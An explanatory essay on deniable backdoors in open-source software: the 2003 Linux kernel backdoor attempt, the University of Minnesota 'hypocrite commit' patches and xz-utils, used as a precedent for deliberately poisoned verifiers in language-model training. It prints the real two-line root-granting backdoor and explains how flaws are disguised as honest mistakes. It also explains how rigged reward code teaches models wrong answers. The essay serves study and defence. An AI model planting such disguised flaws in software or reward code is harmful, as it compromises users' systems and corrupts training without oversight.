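# Deniable backdoors in open-source software as a precedent for poisoned verifiers

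## What are a deniable backdoor and a verifier?

A deniable backdoor is a deliberate security hole in a program, written to look like an honest mistake. Much of the public evidence on such sabotage comes from open-source software, whose code anyone may read and propose changes to. Three cases stand out: a 2003 attempt to insert a backdoor into the Linux kernel (the core of the operating system), a set of flawed test patches that University of Minnesota researchers sent to the kernel's developers and disclosed in 2020, and the 2024 backdoor in xz-utils, a widely used compression package.

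A verifier is a newer kind of program that can raise the same suspicion. It scores a language model's answers during training, and the model learns to produce whatever scores well. If the verifier accepts wrong answers, training can reward them, and someone with access to the verifier could cause this on purpose.

### How a change gets into open-source software

A developer who wants to change a project writes a patch, a proposed change to the source code with a short explanation. A maintainer, someone with authority to accept changes, reads it and may ask for corrections. Once accepted, the patch becomes a commit, a change recorded in the project's repository, whose history is kept by a version control system such as Git. Many projects also run automated tests on each commit and block changes that break a test (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, *Not In My Git Yard*, 2026). The maintainers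 periodically package the current code as a release. Distributors download this package as an archive called the release tarball, which can differ from the public repository because packaging commonly adds files that the repository does not hold.

Code review on a large project depends on trusting people as well as reading code. The Linux kernel documentation's *How the development process works* describes a new release every two or three months, each with about 13,000 changes. Only Linus Torvalds, who created Linux, can merge changes into the main repository. In one release, he picked 112 of the more than 9,500 patches himself. The rest reached him through maintainers who each look after one part of the kernel and take patches from maintainers below them. The documentation calls this a "chain of trust". Torvalds sometimes looks closely at the patches he receives, but he usually relies on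 the people who send them.

It is therefore important to record a change's provenance, meaning who made it, when, by what route and with whose approval. In 2003 every change to the kernel's master copy carried a pointer to the record of its approval, according to the CITP Blog's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*. A reader of the code could check how a line had got there separately from what it did.

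### Vulnerability, backdoor, deniable backdoor

A vulnerability is any weakness in a system that an attacker can exploit, whether or not someone put it there on purpose. A backdoor is a hidden function that gives anyone who knows about it access or powers they should not have. Kokkonis and colleagues mention a clearly deliberate one in vsFTPd, a file-transfer server. For several days around 2011, its official distribution site offered a tampered version, and anyone who typed a smiley face as the user name got a command line with full control of the machine.

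Thomas and Francillon's *Backdoors* splits a backdoor into four parts: an input source, a trigger, a payload and a privileged state. In vsFTPd these would be the network connection, the smiley face, the code that opens the command line, and full control. If the program's own code spells out the step from trigger to payload, the backdoor is intentional, and its makers can't claim it was an accident. But sometimes that step happens only because of a bug, as when an overlong input spills into memory that the program uses for something else. Then the code is the same whether its author was malicious or careless. Thomas and Francillon call such a flaw an accidental vulnerability when no evidence points to intent, and a deniable backdoor when evidence from outside the code allows someone to argue for intent. They conclude that nobody can tell the two apart on purely technical grounds.

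Their definition depends on what an investigator can argue. Defined more plainly, by what the saboteur did, a deniable backdoor is one written so that, if found, it can pass for an honest mistake. Some security writers call this a "bugdoor". *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024), an early analysis of the xz-utils case, predicts that such backdoors will remain possible even if projects adopt every defence it proposes, because old build tools and error-prone programming languages give a saboteur so many plausible mistakes to imitate.

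Thomas and Francillon also analyzed eleven real backdoors, and none met their definition of deniable. Saboteurs may rarely try to make their backdoors deniable. But a deniable backdoor that worked as intended would be listed in the public databases as a bug, so a collection of known backdoors would probably not include it.

### What deniability gives a saboteur

*Defending Against Crypto Backdoors* (Schneier on Security, 2013), an essay by the cryptographer Bruce Schneier, lists three properties an intelligence agency would want in a backdoor: it should be hard to discover, few people should know of it, and "if discovered, the backdoor should look like a mistake."

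Deniability helps the saboteur after the flaw is discovered. If it looks like a mistake, somebody reports it, a maintainer writes a fix and users update, all without anyone needing to ask why the author wrote the line. The saboteur may lose only that flaw and keep the account, the reputation, any other flaws already in place and the chance to try again. When a backdoor is obvious, the saboteur can lose the account too. *xz backdoor*, by Lasse Collin, the original maintainer of xz-utils (writing as Larhzu, 2024), reports that the hosting site GitHub suspended both the account behind the attack and Collin's own, and only later reinstated Collin's.

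Delay also makes a backdoor easier to deny. GitHub's *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021) found that vulnerabilities often went unnoticed for more than four years before disclosure, while a fix typically followed in just over four weeks once somebody had identified the problem. After four years, an author can easily have forgotten why they wrote a line a certain way, so a dishonest author can plausibly claim to have forgotten too.

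The disguise works mainly because the innocent explanation is usually right. GitHub took a random sample of 521 security advisories and classed 17% as explicitly malicious, most of them in little-used packages. Malicious flaws accounted for only 0.2% of the alerts it sent to developers. A maintainer who assumes a bug is a mistake will therefore seldom be wrong, while treating every bug as deliberate would mean accusing many innocent volunteers. However, the 17% includes only malice that somebody could recognise. GitHub concedes that a good backdoor can be indistinguishable from a normal programming error, so some of the remaining 83% could be sabotage, and nobody can estimate how much from this sample.

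Deniability has a drawback for the saboteur. Thomas and Francillon note that the maker of a backdoor that rests on an ordinary bug has no control over how it is used. Anyone else who finds the bug can exploit it.

### Intruder, outside contributor, trusted maintainer

What a saboteur has to get past depends on his or her standing in the project.

An intruder breaks into a machine that holds the code. In 2003, someone apparently broke into a server with a secondary copy of the Linux kernel's source and inserted two lines there. An intruder avoids review, but the change has no record of approval.

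An outside contributor has no authority either, and can only send a patch and hope that a maintainer accepts it. The Minnesota researchers did this as an experiment. Wu and Lu (2020), in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*, describe sending the kernel's developers three patches of fewer than five lines each from a random email account. The researchers used "hypocrite commit" to mean a patch that fixes something minor while introducing a worse flaw. By their account, they stopped all three patches before any became a commit. A maintainer can learn very little from even complete provenance in such cases, because a stranger can easily invent a name and address.

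A trusted maintainer can accept changes, often including their own, and may also build the releases. "Jia Tan", the name behind the xz-utils backdoor, held this position. The *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) reports that whoever used the name spent more than two years as a diligent contributor and gained maintainer's rights during that time. Jia Tan then built and signed the two release tarballs that carried the backdoor. The signatures accurately showed only that someone authorised by the project had signed the releases.

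An attacker can move from one position to another. Jia Tan, the xz-utils attacker, sent a first patch in October 2021 as an ordinary outside contributor and later became a maintainer. An attacker's position is separate from the route by which the malicious code gets in. Kokkonis and colleagues sort past incidents by route, into malicious commits, tampered release packages and compromised dependencies (components that other programs rely on). Jia Tan used all three.

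### How a verifier trains a model

In reinforcement learning, a model (the policy) produces answers, each answer receives a score (the reward), and training adjusts the model to make high-scoring answers more likely. In reinforcement learning with verifiable rewards (RLVR), the reward comes from an automated check rather than a human's opinion, and the program or model that does the checking is called the verifier. According to *Verifier Errors in RLVR* (2026), a verifier usually either compares the response with a known solution or runs the code in the response against tests. Some verifiers are language models that act as judges.

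Suppose the task is to write a function that returns the largest number in a list. The policy writes eight programs. The verifier runs each on three tests: [3, 1, 2] must give 3, [5] must give 5, and [2, 9, 4] must give 9. A program that passes all three earns a reward of 1, and any other program earns 0. Say two of the eight pass.

A common training method, Group Relative Policy Optimization (GRPO), then compares each program with its group. Gupta and Joshi (2026), in *Checking the Checkers*, give the formula, which without a small constant that prevents division by zero is

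advantage = (reward − group mean) / group standard deviation

The mean here is 0.25 and the standard deviation is about 0.43, so each passing program gets an advantage of about +1.73 and each failing one about −0.58. Training raises the probability of the text in the two passing programs and lowers the probability of the text in the other six. The policy then writes more programs, and the loop repeats.

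One of the two programs that passed all three tests starts with zero as the "largest so far" and replaces it whenever it finds a bigger number. Given the list −4, −2, it returns 0, which is not in the list. The program is wrong, but it received the same +1.73 as the correct one.

A false positive is a wrong answer that the verifier rewards. Ray (2026), in *Before the Model Learns the Bug*, writes this as A(c) = 1 and T(c) = 0, where A(c) is 1 if the verifier accepts answer c and T(c) is 1 if c is correct. A false negative is a right answer that the verifier rejects. Gupta and Joshi give the example of a checker that compares strings of characters and can reject "0.5" because the answer key has "1/2".

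Test suites are prone to false positives because a test can show that a program is wrong but cannot prove that it is right. *Negative-Only Policy Optimization for One-Sided Verifiable Rewards* (2026) states that passing the public tests is necessary but not sufficient for correctness. Real suites can have about as few tests as the example. In *When the Reward Suite Is Leaky*, Zhang (2026) worked with a standard set of programming tasks that has about three tests per task, while an extended version has about 105. Zhang also stresses that these errors persist, because the same wrong program passes the same weak tests every time it appears, whereas random scoring errors tend to cancel out over a long run.

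Persistence matters most when the policy can learn to trigger the error. A false positive is exploitable if it depends on some feature of the answer, such as a phrase or a format, that the policy can reproduce often enough for training to reinforce it. Ray points out that the policy only needs to receive the verifier's rewards repeatedly, without seeing its source code.

### A bug or a poisoned verifier?

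A verifier usually depends on tests, answer keys and scripts. Reward code is the verifier together with these, and a fault in any of them can change the score. In Ray's description, the software parses the model's output, extracts an answer, compares values, runs tests, enforces time limits and decides on a reward. People write and revise reward code as they do other software, so it can have a verifier bug, which makes the verifier wrong by accident, or contain a poisoned verifier, which someone made wrong deliberately.

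The parallel with backdoors is inexact because a backdoor serves someone who knows about it and later uses it, while a false positive in reward code affects the policy during training even if nobody knows it is there.

Intent is about as hard to prove in both cases, though. None of the three tests in the example uses a list of negative numbers. A hurried author could have forgotten that case, or someone could have left it out on purpose. The test file and the rewards would be identical either way. When a verifier is found to reward wrong answers, can anyone establish whether the cause was a bug or poisoning, and do the cases of Linux, Minnesota and xz-utils help?

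## How was the 2003 Linux backdoor disguised and caught?

In November 2003, an intruder added two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code. The lines looked like an error check, but they would have let any user of an affected machine take complete control of it. The kernel's developers worked out what the lines did on their public mailing list, where anyone can still read the discussion.

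### The main repository and its copy

At the time, Torvalds kept the kernel in BitKeeper, a version control system made by BitMover. Some developers refused to use BitKeeper because it was proprietary, so BitMover published a second copy of the code for them in CVS, an older, free system. Isaacson (2003) explains in *attempt to plant a back door in the Linux kernel* that code flowed automatically only from BitKeeper to CVS. A change in the CVS copy could reach Torvalds only if a developer sent it to him as a patch.

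Larry McVoy (2003) describes how BitMover, the company he founded, made the copy in *BK2CVS problem*, the thread where the discovery took place. A scheduled job fetched the BitKeeper code, converted it to CVS on a machine inside BitMover and copied the updated files to the public server. It then compared checksums of the public files with checksums of BitMover's own files. A checksum is a short number calculated from a file's contents, and even a one-character edit will almost certainly change it. The comparison ran every night without anyone having to understand the code, and it sent an email if anything differed.

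The conversion also added a pointer, such as "(Logical change 1.14141)", to each entry in the CVS change log to identify the BitKeeper change it came from.

### Two lines that look like an error check

These are the two lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The intruder put them in the code for wait4, a request a program makes to pause until another program has finished. "options" holds the settings sent with the request, and `__WCLONE` and `__WALL` are two settings that nobody would normally combine. "current->uid" is the number of the user running the program, and 0 is the number for root, the administrator, who may do anything on the machine. "EINVAL" is the error code for an invalid request. A quick reader would therefore take the lines to mean that the kernel should refuse this odd combination if root sends it.

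In the C programming language, two equals signs compare values, and one assigns a value. So "current->uid == 0" checks whether the user is root, while "current->uid = 0" makes the user root.

Suppose user number 1000 runs a program that sends the odd combination. The first half of the test is true, so the computer goes on to the second half, which changes the user's number from 1000 to 0. In C, an assignment takes the value that was assigned, here 0, which counts as false. The whole test therefore fails, the second line never runs, and the program carries on as root without an "invalid request" error. With any other settings, the computer skips the second half of the test, so ordinary use would not have revealed the flaw.

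The person who wrote the backdoor knew the kernel well. McVoy told Poulsen (2003, *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks*) that its author had to find settings that the kernel would accept together but that programs don't normally combine. The backdoor would only have helped an attacker who could already run a program on the target machine (Corbet, 2003, *The upcoming security fight*).

Programmers often type one equals sign where they mean two, and the compiler, which turns source code into a runnable program, normally warns about it. An extra pair of parentheses around the assignment turns the warning off. The developer Tomas Szepe noticed the same night that the intruder's line had this extra pair. Gervase Markham, in *Comments on "An attempt to backdoor the kernel"* (2003), concluded that the attacker must have known about the warning.

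The parentheses are weaker evidence of intent than they seem. A commenter on the blog Freedom to Tinker pointed out that the line would not compile without them, and that programmers often put parentheses around comparisons anyway. The first comparison in the line has a pair it doesn't need. Someone who meant to type two equals signs and dropped one could have written exactly the same line, and the compiler would not have warned them either.

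More suspiciously, the lines were useless as an error check. Chad Kitching, another developer on the list, saw that the next line of the existing code overwrites the error code, so the check would have done nothing even with the second equals sign in place. But careless programmers write useless code too. The security consultant Ryan Russell told Poulsen that the change was "indistinguishable from an accidental bug" unless somebody had a reason to find out whether it had been legitimately checked in.

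### The name and the "Oops"

The intruder disguised the change log as well as the code. Three false entries appeared there, dated 4 November:

- At 16:22:47, two lines added, with no message.
- At 16:42:00, 58 lines removed, with no message.
- At 16:44:19, 58 lines added, with the message "Oops, I worked on the the wrong file, fixed again."

After all three changes, the file differed from the genuine one only in the backdoor's two lines. Nobody has explained why the intruder took 58 lines out and put them back. It may have been an accident, but it meant that anyone who glanced at the top of the log would see a developer apologising for a harmless mistake and reporting that it was fixed.

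All three entries carried the user name of David Miller, a well-known kernel developer. A trusted name makes people less likely to question a change, but it gave the intruder little protection once people started asking about this one. Miller denied making the edits, and the others believed him. In the LWN *Comments*, a reader called Max.Hyre asked whether anyone would have believed the denial if the intruder had picked a newcomer who had just received permission to commit changes. Max.Hyre also asked whether some doubt would have remained even if people had believed the newcomer.

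### From "not a big deal" to a backdoor

McVoy saw the failed comparison on the morning of 5 November, California time. He first suspected his own export software and ran tests to rule it out. Then he restored the file and wrote to the mailing list. By his account, the checksums had flagged the file, and the three newest entries in its log had no pointer to a BitKeeper change because somebody had edited the public copy directly. He asked whoever was responsible to come forward, and said it was "not a big deal", though annoying for people who used CVS.

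The messages that followed, with times in UTC, were these:

| Time | Message |
|---|---|
| 20:45 | McVoy reports the unexplained edits |
| 20:58 | Matthew Dharm asks, out of curiosity, which lines changed |
| 22:23 | McVoy posts the two lines |
| 22:33 | Zwane Mwaikambo replies, "That looks odd" |
| 22:48 | Kitching asks whether it is an attempt to backdoor the kernel |
| 22:51 | Andries Brouwer answers Mwaikambo: "Not if you hope to get root." |
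| 23:03 | McVoy agrees with Kitching: "Good eyes, I missed that." |

Someone on the mailing list recognized the backdoor about two hours after the first report, but only 25 minutes after McVoy posted the code. Until he posted it, no one else on the list could read the lines.

Even McVoy missed the assignment, though he had the two lines isolated in front of him and knew that nobody had approved them. In *Thwarted Linux backdoor*, Jones (2003) applied the case to voting machines. Voting software standards already forbade assignments inside a test, and automatic checks were good at finding them, so those checks would have flagged this line. But Jones expected that an attacker this skilled would have followed the coding rules and hidden the flaw some other way.

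It is less clear how long the lines had been there. McVoy told the list that BitMover had found and corrected the problem in under 24 hours. Route Fifty's *Effort to compromise Linux kernel foiled* (2003) gives his estimate that the change went in at about 2 a.m. on 5 November, four hours before BitMover discovered it. But the log entries are dated 4 November, and if their times are in UTC, more than 28 hours passed between the first edit and the first report. The log was on a machine that the intruder had broken into, so its times may be unreliable.

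People also disagreed about who deserved the credit. Some press coverage cited the open-source principle that many eyes find bugs. Fourteen years later, McVoy (2017), in *History of exploits*, was still annoyed by this and insisted that his eyes had found the backdoor. He is right about the detection, which came from a comparison he had set up because he trusted nothing. But other people recognised the backdoor when they read the lines on the list.

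### How close did it come?

Torvalds answered "No" when asked whether the change could have reached a kernel release. Some developers emailed him patches, and he said that any patch to a core file would be read and need an explanation. Developers who merged their work through BitKeeper wouldn't have been using the CVS copy.

Theodore Ts'o, another senior kernel developer, agreed about official releases but thought the backdoor might have reached users another way, if a distributor (an organisation that packages Linux for users) was building its kernel from the CVS copy. Corbet thought it unlikely that any did, and the distributor Debian lists its own kernel as unaffected on its page about the flaw, *CVE-2003-1161*.

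A reader of the news site LWN, iabervon (2003), described a third possibility in *An attempt to backdoor the kernel*. A trusted developer might download the altered file, work on it, and unknowingly send Torvalds the two lines in the middle of a larger patch. BitMover's next export would meanwhile have overwritten the false entries in the public copy. If anyone later found the backdoor, the audit trail would have led only to the innocent developer. Another reader, proski, objected that the CVS command for listing one's own changes leaves out changes made by other people. iabervon had already tried to answer this objection by arguing that, once the export had erased the intruder's entries, CVS would treat the lines as the developer's own.

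McVoy, whose company BitMover sold BitKeeper, told Route Fifty that somebody else would have caught the change if BitMover hadn't. But in the LWN comments, he wrote that the flaw would probably already be in the kernel if a free tool had been used instead of BitKeeper.

Few people could have picked up the altered file. McVoy reported in *kernel.bkbits.net off the air* (2003) that only about six internet addresses were using the CVS server when he last checked. H. Peter Anvin, who maintained another copy at kernel.org, replied that this left out anyone using that copy, but he doubted that the omission mattered in the time available. The small number of users and the short exposure are better reasons to think the attempt would have failed than Torvalds's confidence in review. In iabervon's scenario, a reviewer would have had to notice the missing equals sign inside a longer patch from a trusted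 colleague. McVoy overlooked the same error in two lines he already knew were unauthorised.

### An unidentified intruder

Nobody has publicly identified the culprit. McVoy said the attack had come through a university computer that a third party had hacked. How the intruder got into BitMover's server is also unknown. In May 2003, after a disk failure, McVoy had reinstalled the server's operating system without security fixes, which he left for "Dave" to install, and said so on the public mailing list. Harkes (2003), in *and BK->CVS gateway*, objected at once and listed seven programs, including CVS, with holes that an attacker could use remotely. The published messages don't establish whether any of those holes was still open in November.

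McVoy took the server offline to examine its disks. He gave up after three days, still unable to read all the data, and suspected that the intruder had hidden something in the file system. Anvin (2003), in *data from kernel.bkbits.net*, thought the errors looked more like a bug in the driver, the software that controls the disks. The investigation therefore also raised the question of whether a fault was malicious or accidental.

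The intruder's motive is also unknown. Corbet suspected a publicity stunt, since a backdoor that worked only for people already on the machine would have been more useful for embarrassing Linux than for breaking into computers. Woods (2003), in the same discussion as Isaacson, suggested that the intruder may have targeted only people who used the CVS copy and never meant the lines to reach Torvalds.

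### Origin first, then purpose

The nightly comparison worked because BitMover had an original that the intruder hadn't touched. It showed that the two lines had come from outside the normal process, but their purpose became clear only when people read them. McVoy had at first treated them as a nuisance.

The missing record also made an innocent explanation less plausible. If the file had matched its original, the single equals sign under Miller's name could have passed for a typing error. Someone who broke into a server and used another developer's name is much less likely to have made the change by accident. A commenter on Freedom to Tinker suggested that a tired developer with access to the server might have skipped the approval process, but nobody came forward when McVoy asked.

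A comparison like this can't catch a bad change that the main repository has already accepted, because the copy will match. The day after the discovery, Ts'o warned on the list that someone might send Torvalds a small patch that was presented as a bug fix but created a vulnerability. The sender could forge a trusted developer's name and hide the patch among other plausible changes. Ts'o proposed that developers sign their changes digitally, which he had been urging on McVoy for years. Signatures would have exposed a forged name, but they would not have stopped someone from sending the same patch under a name of their own.

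## What did the University of Minnesota's patches show about code review?

In August 2020 Qiushi Wu, a doctoral student at the University of Minnesota, and Wu's supervisor, Kangjie Lu, tried an attack much like the one Ts'o had warned about. They did not tell the kernel's maintainers.

People often confuse three separate events:

- In August 2020 Wu and Lu sent deliberately flawed patches under false names.
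- In November 2020 they announced that the IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy (IEEE S&P), a leading computer security conference, had accepted their paper about the experiment. They withdrew it in April 2021.
- In April 2021 Aditya Pakki, another doctoral student in Lu's group, sent the kernel some poor patches openly. They had nothing to do with the experiment, but they led the senior kernel developer Greg Kroah-Hartman to ban the whole university.

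So the patches that triggered the ban were honest, while the deliberately flawed ones had aroused no suspicion when they arrived.

### How the experiment was supposed to work

In *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, Wu and Lu wanted to show that a stranger could get a vulnerability into the kernel while appearing to fix something trivial. Each of their short patches was also meant to complete an "immature vulnerability", their term for a security hole that still lacks one necessary condition.

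The vulnerability in this experiment was a use-after-free. A program reserves a block of memory when it needs one and frees it when finished. If the program uses the block after that, something else may already be stored there, and an attacker can sometimes exploit the error. A patch can create this vulnerability by adding a use of a block that existing code has already freed, or by freeing a block too early. Either change can look like routine cleanup to a reviewer.

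Honest programmers make this kind of mistake too. Wu and Lu collected 138 publicly catalogued kernel vulnerabilities introduced by patches of fewer than 30 lines, and they write that the submitters meant no harm. Such small fixes caused almost a tenth of the vulnerabilities they examined.

To keep their own flaws out of the kernel, Wu and Lu planned to wait until a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, then immediately point out the flaw and send a correct version. The plan depended on there being time between a maintainer's approval and the commit. In their paper and their December 2020 FAQ, they reported that it had worked in all three cases and that the maintainers had agreed each time not to go ahead with the flawed patch.

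### Three, four or five patches?

The emails don't support that account. The researchers published them after the ban, in the University of Minnesota's *A Full Disclosure of the Case Study of the “Hypocrite Commits” Paper* (2021). The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board (TAB), a group of kernel developers, investigated as well. Its report of 5 May 2021, which the kernel developer Pavel Machek quoted on the mailing list, lists the same five patches:

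| Sent (2020) | False name | Stated purpose | Flawed? | In the paper? | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 August | James Bond | Fix a leak in firmware code | No | No | Nobody took it up |
| 9 August | James Bond | Fix a memory leak in console code | Yes | Yes | A maintainer rejected it within hours |
| 20 August | George Acosta | Add a missing error message | No, though the researchers thought so | Yes | A maintainer accepted it |
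| 20 August | George Acosta | Correct a usage count in a device driver | Yes | Yes | A reviewer found other faults, and no new version followed |
| 21 August | James Bond | Correct a usage count in another driver | Yes | No | A reviewer suggested changes, and the sender withdrew it |

The totals differ because people counted different patches. The two false accounts sent five. According to the researchers, the first was an ordinary fix sent from the wrong account by mistake. The other four are the study patches in the University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021), and three of them contained a planted flaw. The paper also describes three patches, but it omits the flawed patch of 21 August and includes the harmless error-message patch.

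Later accounts, such as *Retour sur l’affaire des « patchs hypocrites » de l’Université du Minnesota* (gouttegd, 2022), therefore list one patch as accepted and four as rejected or ignored. The accepted patch was the one involving the error message. No maintainer in the published emails approved any of the three flawed patches, so the researchers had no approval to interrupt.

In the disclosure, the researchers concede that the paper should have explained that the error-message patch was harmless. According to gouttegd, the IEEE S&P programme committee found in May 2021 that the description of the patches was ambiguous and in some cases misleading, and that the experiments were inconclusive. Derek Jones, who writes the blog The Shape of Code, complained that the paper never gives the results of its three submissions. Readers could not easily look them up either, because Wu and Lu had removed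 function and variable names to protect the maintainers' identities.

### What the reviewers noticed

Jiri Slaby rejected the console patch of 9 August about seven hours after it arrived, because it looked familiar. Someone else had sent the same maintainers almost the same change in 2019, apparently without realizing it was faulty. A maintainer accepted that patch, but the developers later removed it because it created a use-after-free. Wu and Lu submitted the bug on purpose, but say they didn't know about the earlier patch.

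Slaby's quick answer is weak evidence of whether reviewers would have spotted an unfamiliar flaw. It also undermines the researchers' claim that every patch addressed a real fault, since the maintainers didn't believe there was a leak. Kroah-Hartman wrote "Nice name..." under James Bond's signature and asked the sender to mark the automated bug report as invalid so it wouldn't keep coming up.

Dan Carpenter answered the driver patch of 20 August in under five hours. Carpenter called the function's error handling "kind of rubbish", found a different use-after-free in it and proposed a rewrite, but did not mention the planted flaw. The rewrite would have moved the line the patch added to a safer place, which would probably have removed the flaw without anyone noticing it.

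The maintainer Miquel Raynal replied to the patch of 21 August six days later, suggesting that the new lines go elsewhere in the function, but also missed the planted flaw. The next day the sender, "James Bond", said they had rechecked the function and found the patch "meaningless", and apologised for the bother, admitting the deliberate flaw as though it were an oversight. Raynal replied, "Ok that's fine, thanks anyway!"

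The harmless patch exposed a weakness in the researchers' safeguard. They believed it contained a flaw when they sent it. Herbert Xu's first reply, a week later, was "Patch applied. Thanks." Wu and Lu were relying on a gap between a patch's approval and its addition to a development branch, but Xu had done both in one step. More than 18 hours later, "George Acosta" asked whether two of the function's calls were in the right order, and Xu thought it didn't matter. The researchers say they let the patch go ahead because further checking had shown it to be valid, but they don't say when they checked. If the patch had contained the intended flaw, that flaw would already have been in Xu's branch, though not yet in a kernel release.

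Reviewers recognised the planted flaw in one of the three patches, and none of the three was merged. Three patches are too few to estimate a detection rate. The two patches whose flaws reviewers missed stalled over unrelated faults, and the researchers did not send improved versions. A real attacker could have made the requested changes and resubmitted them.

### How often do reviewers catch such flaws?

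The paper has a second source of evidence, which depends on the kernel's history and not on the experiment. Wu and Lu gathered use-after-free flaws from January 2015 to August 2020 and sorted them into those that maintainers had caught in review and those that had been merged. They then calculated

catch rate = caught / (caught + merged)

Reviewers' baseline catch rate was 56.6%, compared with 19.4% for flaws that involved concurrency, where parts of a program run at the same time and their order can vary. Such flaws are hard to see because the code may work in one order and fail in another.

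Wu and Lu call these figures upper bounds. If reviewers caught 566 flaws and merged another 434 that somebody found later, the catch rate is 566 / 1,000, or 56.6%. If 200 more merged flaws are still undiscovered, the real rate is 566 / 1,200, or about 47%. Since nobody can count the undiscovered flaws, Wu and Lu assumed there were none, which makes the reviewers look better than they were.

This reasoning works only if the researchers counted every flaw that reviewers caught. A reviewer may turn down a bad patch without naming its worst fault, and the sender may then drop it. Carpenter and Raynal each helped stop a flawed patch that way, and neither patch would count as a caught flaw under the paper's definition. If the researchers overlooked many flaws that reviewers had caught, the true catch rate could be higher than theirs. gouttegd distrusts the 56.6% for a different reason, because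 the paper doesn't identify the patches behind it and the researchers had already misdescribed their experiment.

As far as anyone knows, the flaws in these data were honest mistakes. A saboteur could get flaws past reviewers more often than a careless programmer does, by choosing the kind that reviewers tend to miss. As Wu and Lu point out, a saboteur can also try again. If each attempt were independent, the chance that reviewers would catch all three of three flaws at the baseline rate is 0.566³, or about 18%. Real attempts would not be fully independent, because a maintainer might become wary of someone who kept sending bad patches. But the Minnesota researchers used two names for five patches, and nobody objected.

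### Could the researchers have asked permission?

Objections began as soon as Wu and Lu announced the paper in November 2020. According to gouttegd, they wrote in a summary on Twitter that they had introduced exploitable vulnerabilities into the latest kernel. They later apologised, calling the summary misleading. In December four security specialists, including the cryptographer Sarah Jamie Lewis, wrote to the conference to object that the researchers had experimented on people without their consent.

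In their FAQ, Wu and Lu replied that they were studying the patching process, not individual behaviour. They said they had kept the patches very short to save the maintainers' time, but admitted they had wasted some of it. gouttegd answers that the process consists of people. The experiment tested whether the people who read patches would be fooled.

The researchers sent the patches without first consulting the university's review board, which checks studies involving human subjects. They went to the board only after people who had seen the paper's summary told them to. The board decided that the work was not human research and gave them a formal exemption. The paper mentions the exemption but not that it came after the experiment. According to gouttegd, the conference later concluded that the researchers had not given the board enough detail.

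In the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), rmayr, one of the four who had complained, argued that any harm, including wasted time, is unethical if the people affected haven't consented, and that the deception made it worse. Another reader, epa, thought it absurd to compare a bad patch with a medical experiment. epa also pointed out that a bad actor could have sent the same patches without ever disclosing them, and most likely nobody would have noticed.

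The University of Minnesota researchers' best defence was that maintainers who knew about the study would have been on the lookout for the patches, as Lu, Wu and Pakki explained in *An open letter to the Linux community* (2021). Warning maintainers would have made it hard to measure ordinary review, but somebody senior could still have approved the study. Companies do this when they test their staff with fake phishing emails. Two days after the open letter, Wu and Lu (2021) largely accepted this in the letter withdrawing their paper, writing that they should have asked community leaders to approve the goals and methods beforehand.

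Wu had an opportunity to tell the maintainers on 27 August 2020, while two of the patches were still awaiting replies. That day, Wu wrote to the kernel mailing list under their own name to ask how maintainers dealt with "bad" contributors who planted bugs on purpose. In the published message, Wu doesn't mention that their group had been sending such patches. The researchers nevertheless say in the FAQ that they reported their findings to the community before submitting the paper.

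IEEE S&P had also missed the ethical problem. The paper's four reviewers rated it among the top 5% of submissions, according to *An IEEE statement on the UMN paper* (Corbet, 2021). gouttegd adds that one committee member had briefly raised a possible ethical issue, but nobody took it up. The conference announced an ethics review board for the following year.

### An honest patch that looked like sabotage

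On 6 April 2021 Pakki posted a three-line patch for a problem that an experimental code-checking tool had reported. The reviewers did their job. According to LWN, the developer J. Bruce Fields questioned the patch the next day, and Trond Myklebust rejected it the day after that.

On 20 April Kroah-Hartman told Pakki to stop sending patches that Pakki knew to be invalid, and accused Lu of experimenting on the review process to get a paper. Pakki called the accusations defamatory. The next day Kroah-Hartman announced that he would reject all future contributions from the university and remove its earlier ones. In an email reposted in AskWoody's *Linux banned University of Minnesota for sending buggy patches*, he reminded Pakki that the group had publicly admitted sending bad patches on purpose, and asked what he was "supposed to think" now that more were arriving.

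His suspicion was reasonable but mistaken. The university said in its statement that the patches Pakki's project sent on 6 April were superfluous and of poor quality, but submitted in good faith. The TAB had already said on 22 April that the vast majority of the university's patches seemed to be in good faith (Corbet, 2021, *A statement on the UMN mess*).

Thomas and Francillon require evidence from outside the code for a charge of intent. Kroah-Hartman had such evidence in the group's own admission, but the admission was about different patches and led him to the wrong conclusion about these. He could not have discovered his mistake from the code. In the comments on LWN's *An update on the UMN affair* (2021), the kernel developer Al Viro challenged another reader to show that malicious intent leaves any recognisable mark on a patch that would make it easier to catch than an innocent bug.

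The ban was also a poor defence against a repeat of the experiment. Kroah-Hartman's first list of patches to reconsider covered those sent from the university's email addresses, but the flawed patches of August 2020 had come from Gmail accounts. The kernel developers did not yet know this, because Wu and Lu did not identify their patches until 27 April, after the Linux Foundation had demanded it.

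### Re-checking 435 commits

Kroah-Hartman first proposed removing 190 of the university's commits. According to the LWN report quoted by destinyland in *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*, most were acceptable and nearly all addressed some real problem. Removing them all would have brought old bugs back, so developers had to read each one again. By 29 April, only 42 were still due for removal.

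The TAB organised a wider review of 435 commits. Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal* gives the results:

| Finding | Commits |
|---|---|
| Correct | 349 |
| Faulty and still in need of fixing | 39 |
| Already fixed by later commits | 25 |
| No longer relevant | 12 |
| Made before the research group existed | 9 |
| Removed at the author's request | 1 |

gouttegd went through the TAB's full list and counted 442 commits, of which 78, or about 18%, had been faulty when their authors submitted them. None of the 78 was deliberate. gouttegd infers that the maintainers had managed to keep out faulty patches 82% of the time, but that misreads the figure. It means that 82% of the patches they accepted were sound. Nobody counted the faulty patches they had turned away, so the number can't be compared with Wu and Lu's catch rate.

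A commenter on LWN noted that the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board thanked 85 developers in its report. The developers had fixed or removed dozens of ordinary faults, so their work had some value beyond settling whether any faults were deliberate. But they had re-read hundreds of commits because of three flawed patches, none of which had entered the kernel, and they found no sabotage.

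Even this search was incomplete. The university later told the TAB about another Gmail account, which a visiting student had used to send four patches for bugs found by a tool. Maintainers accepted none of them. Kees Cook, who wrote to the mailing list on the TAB's behalf, also said that the TAB had received several questions about whether the researchers had targeted other projects. The university said they had not.

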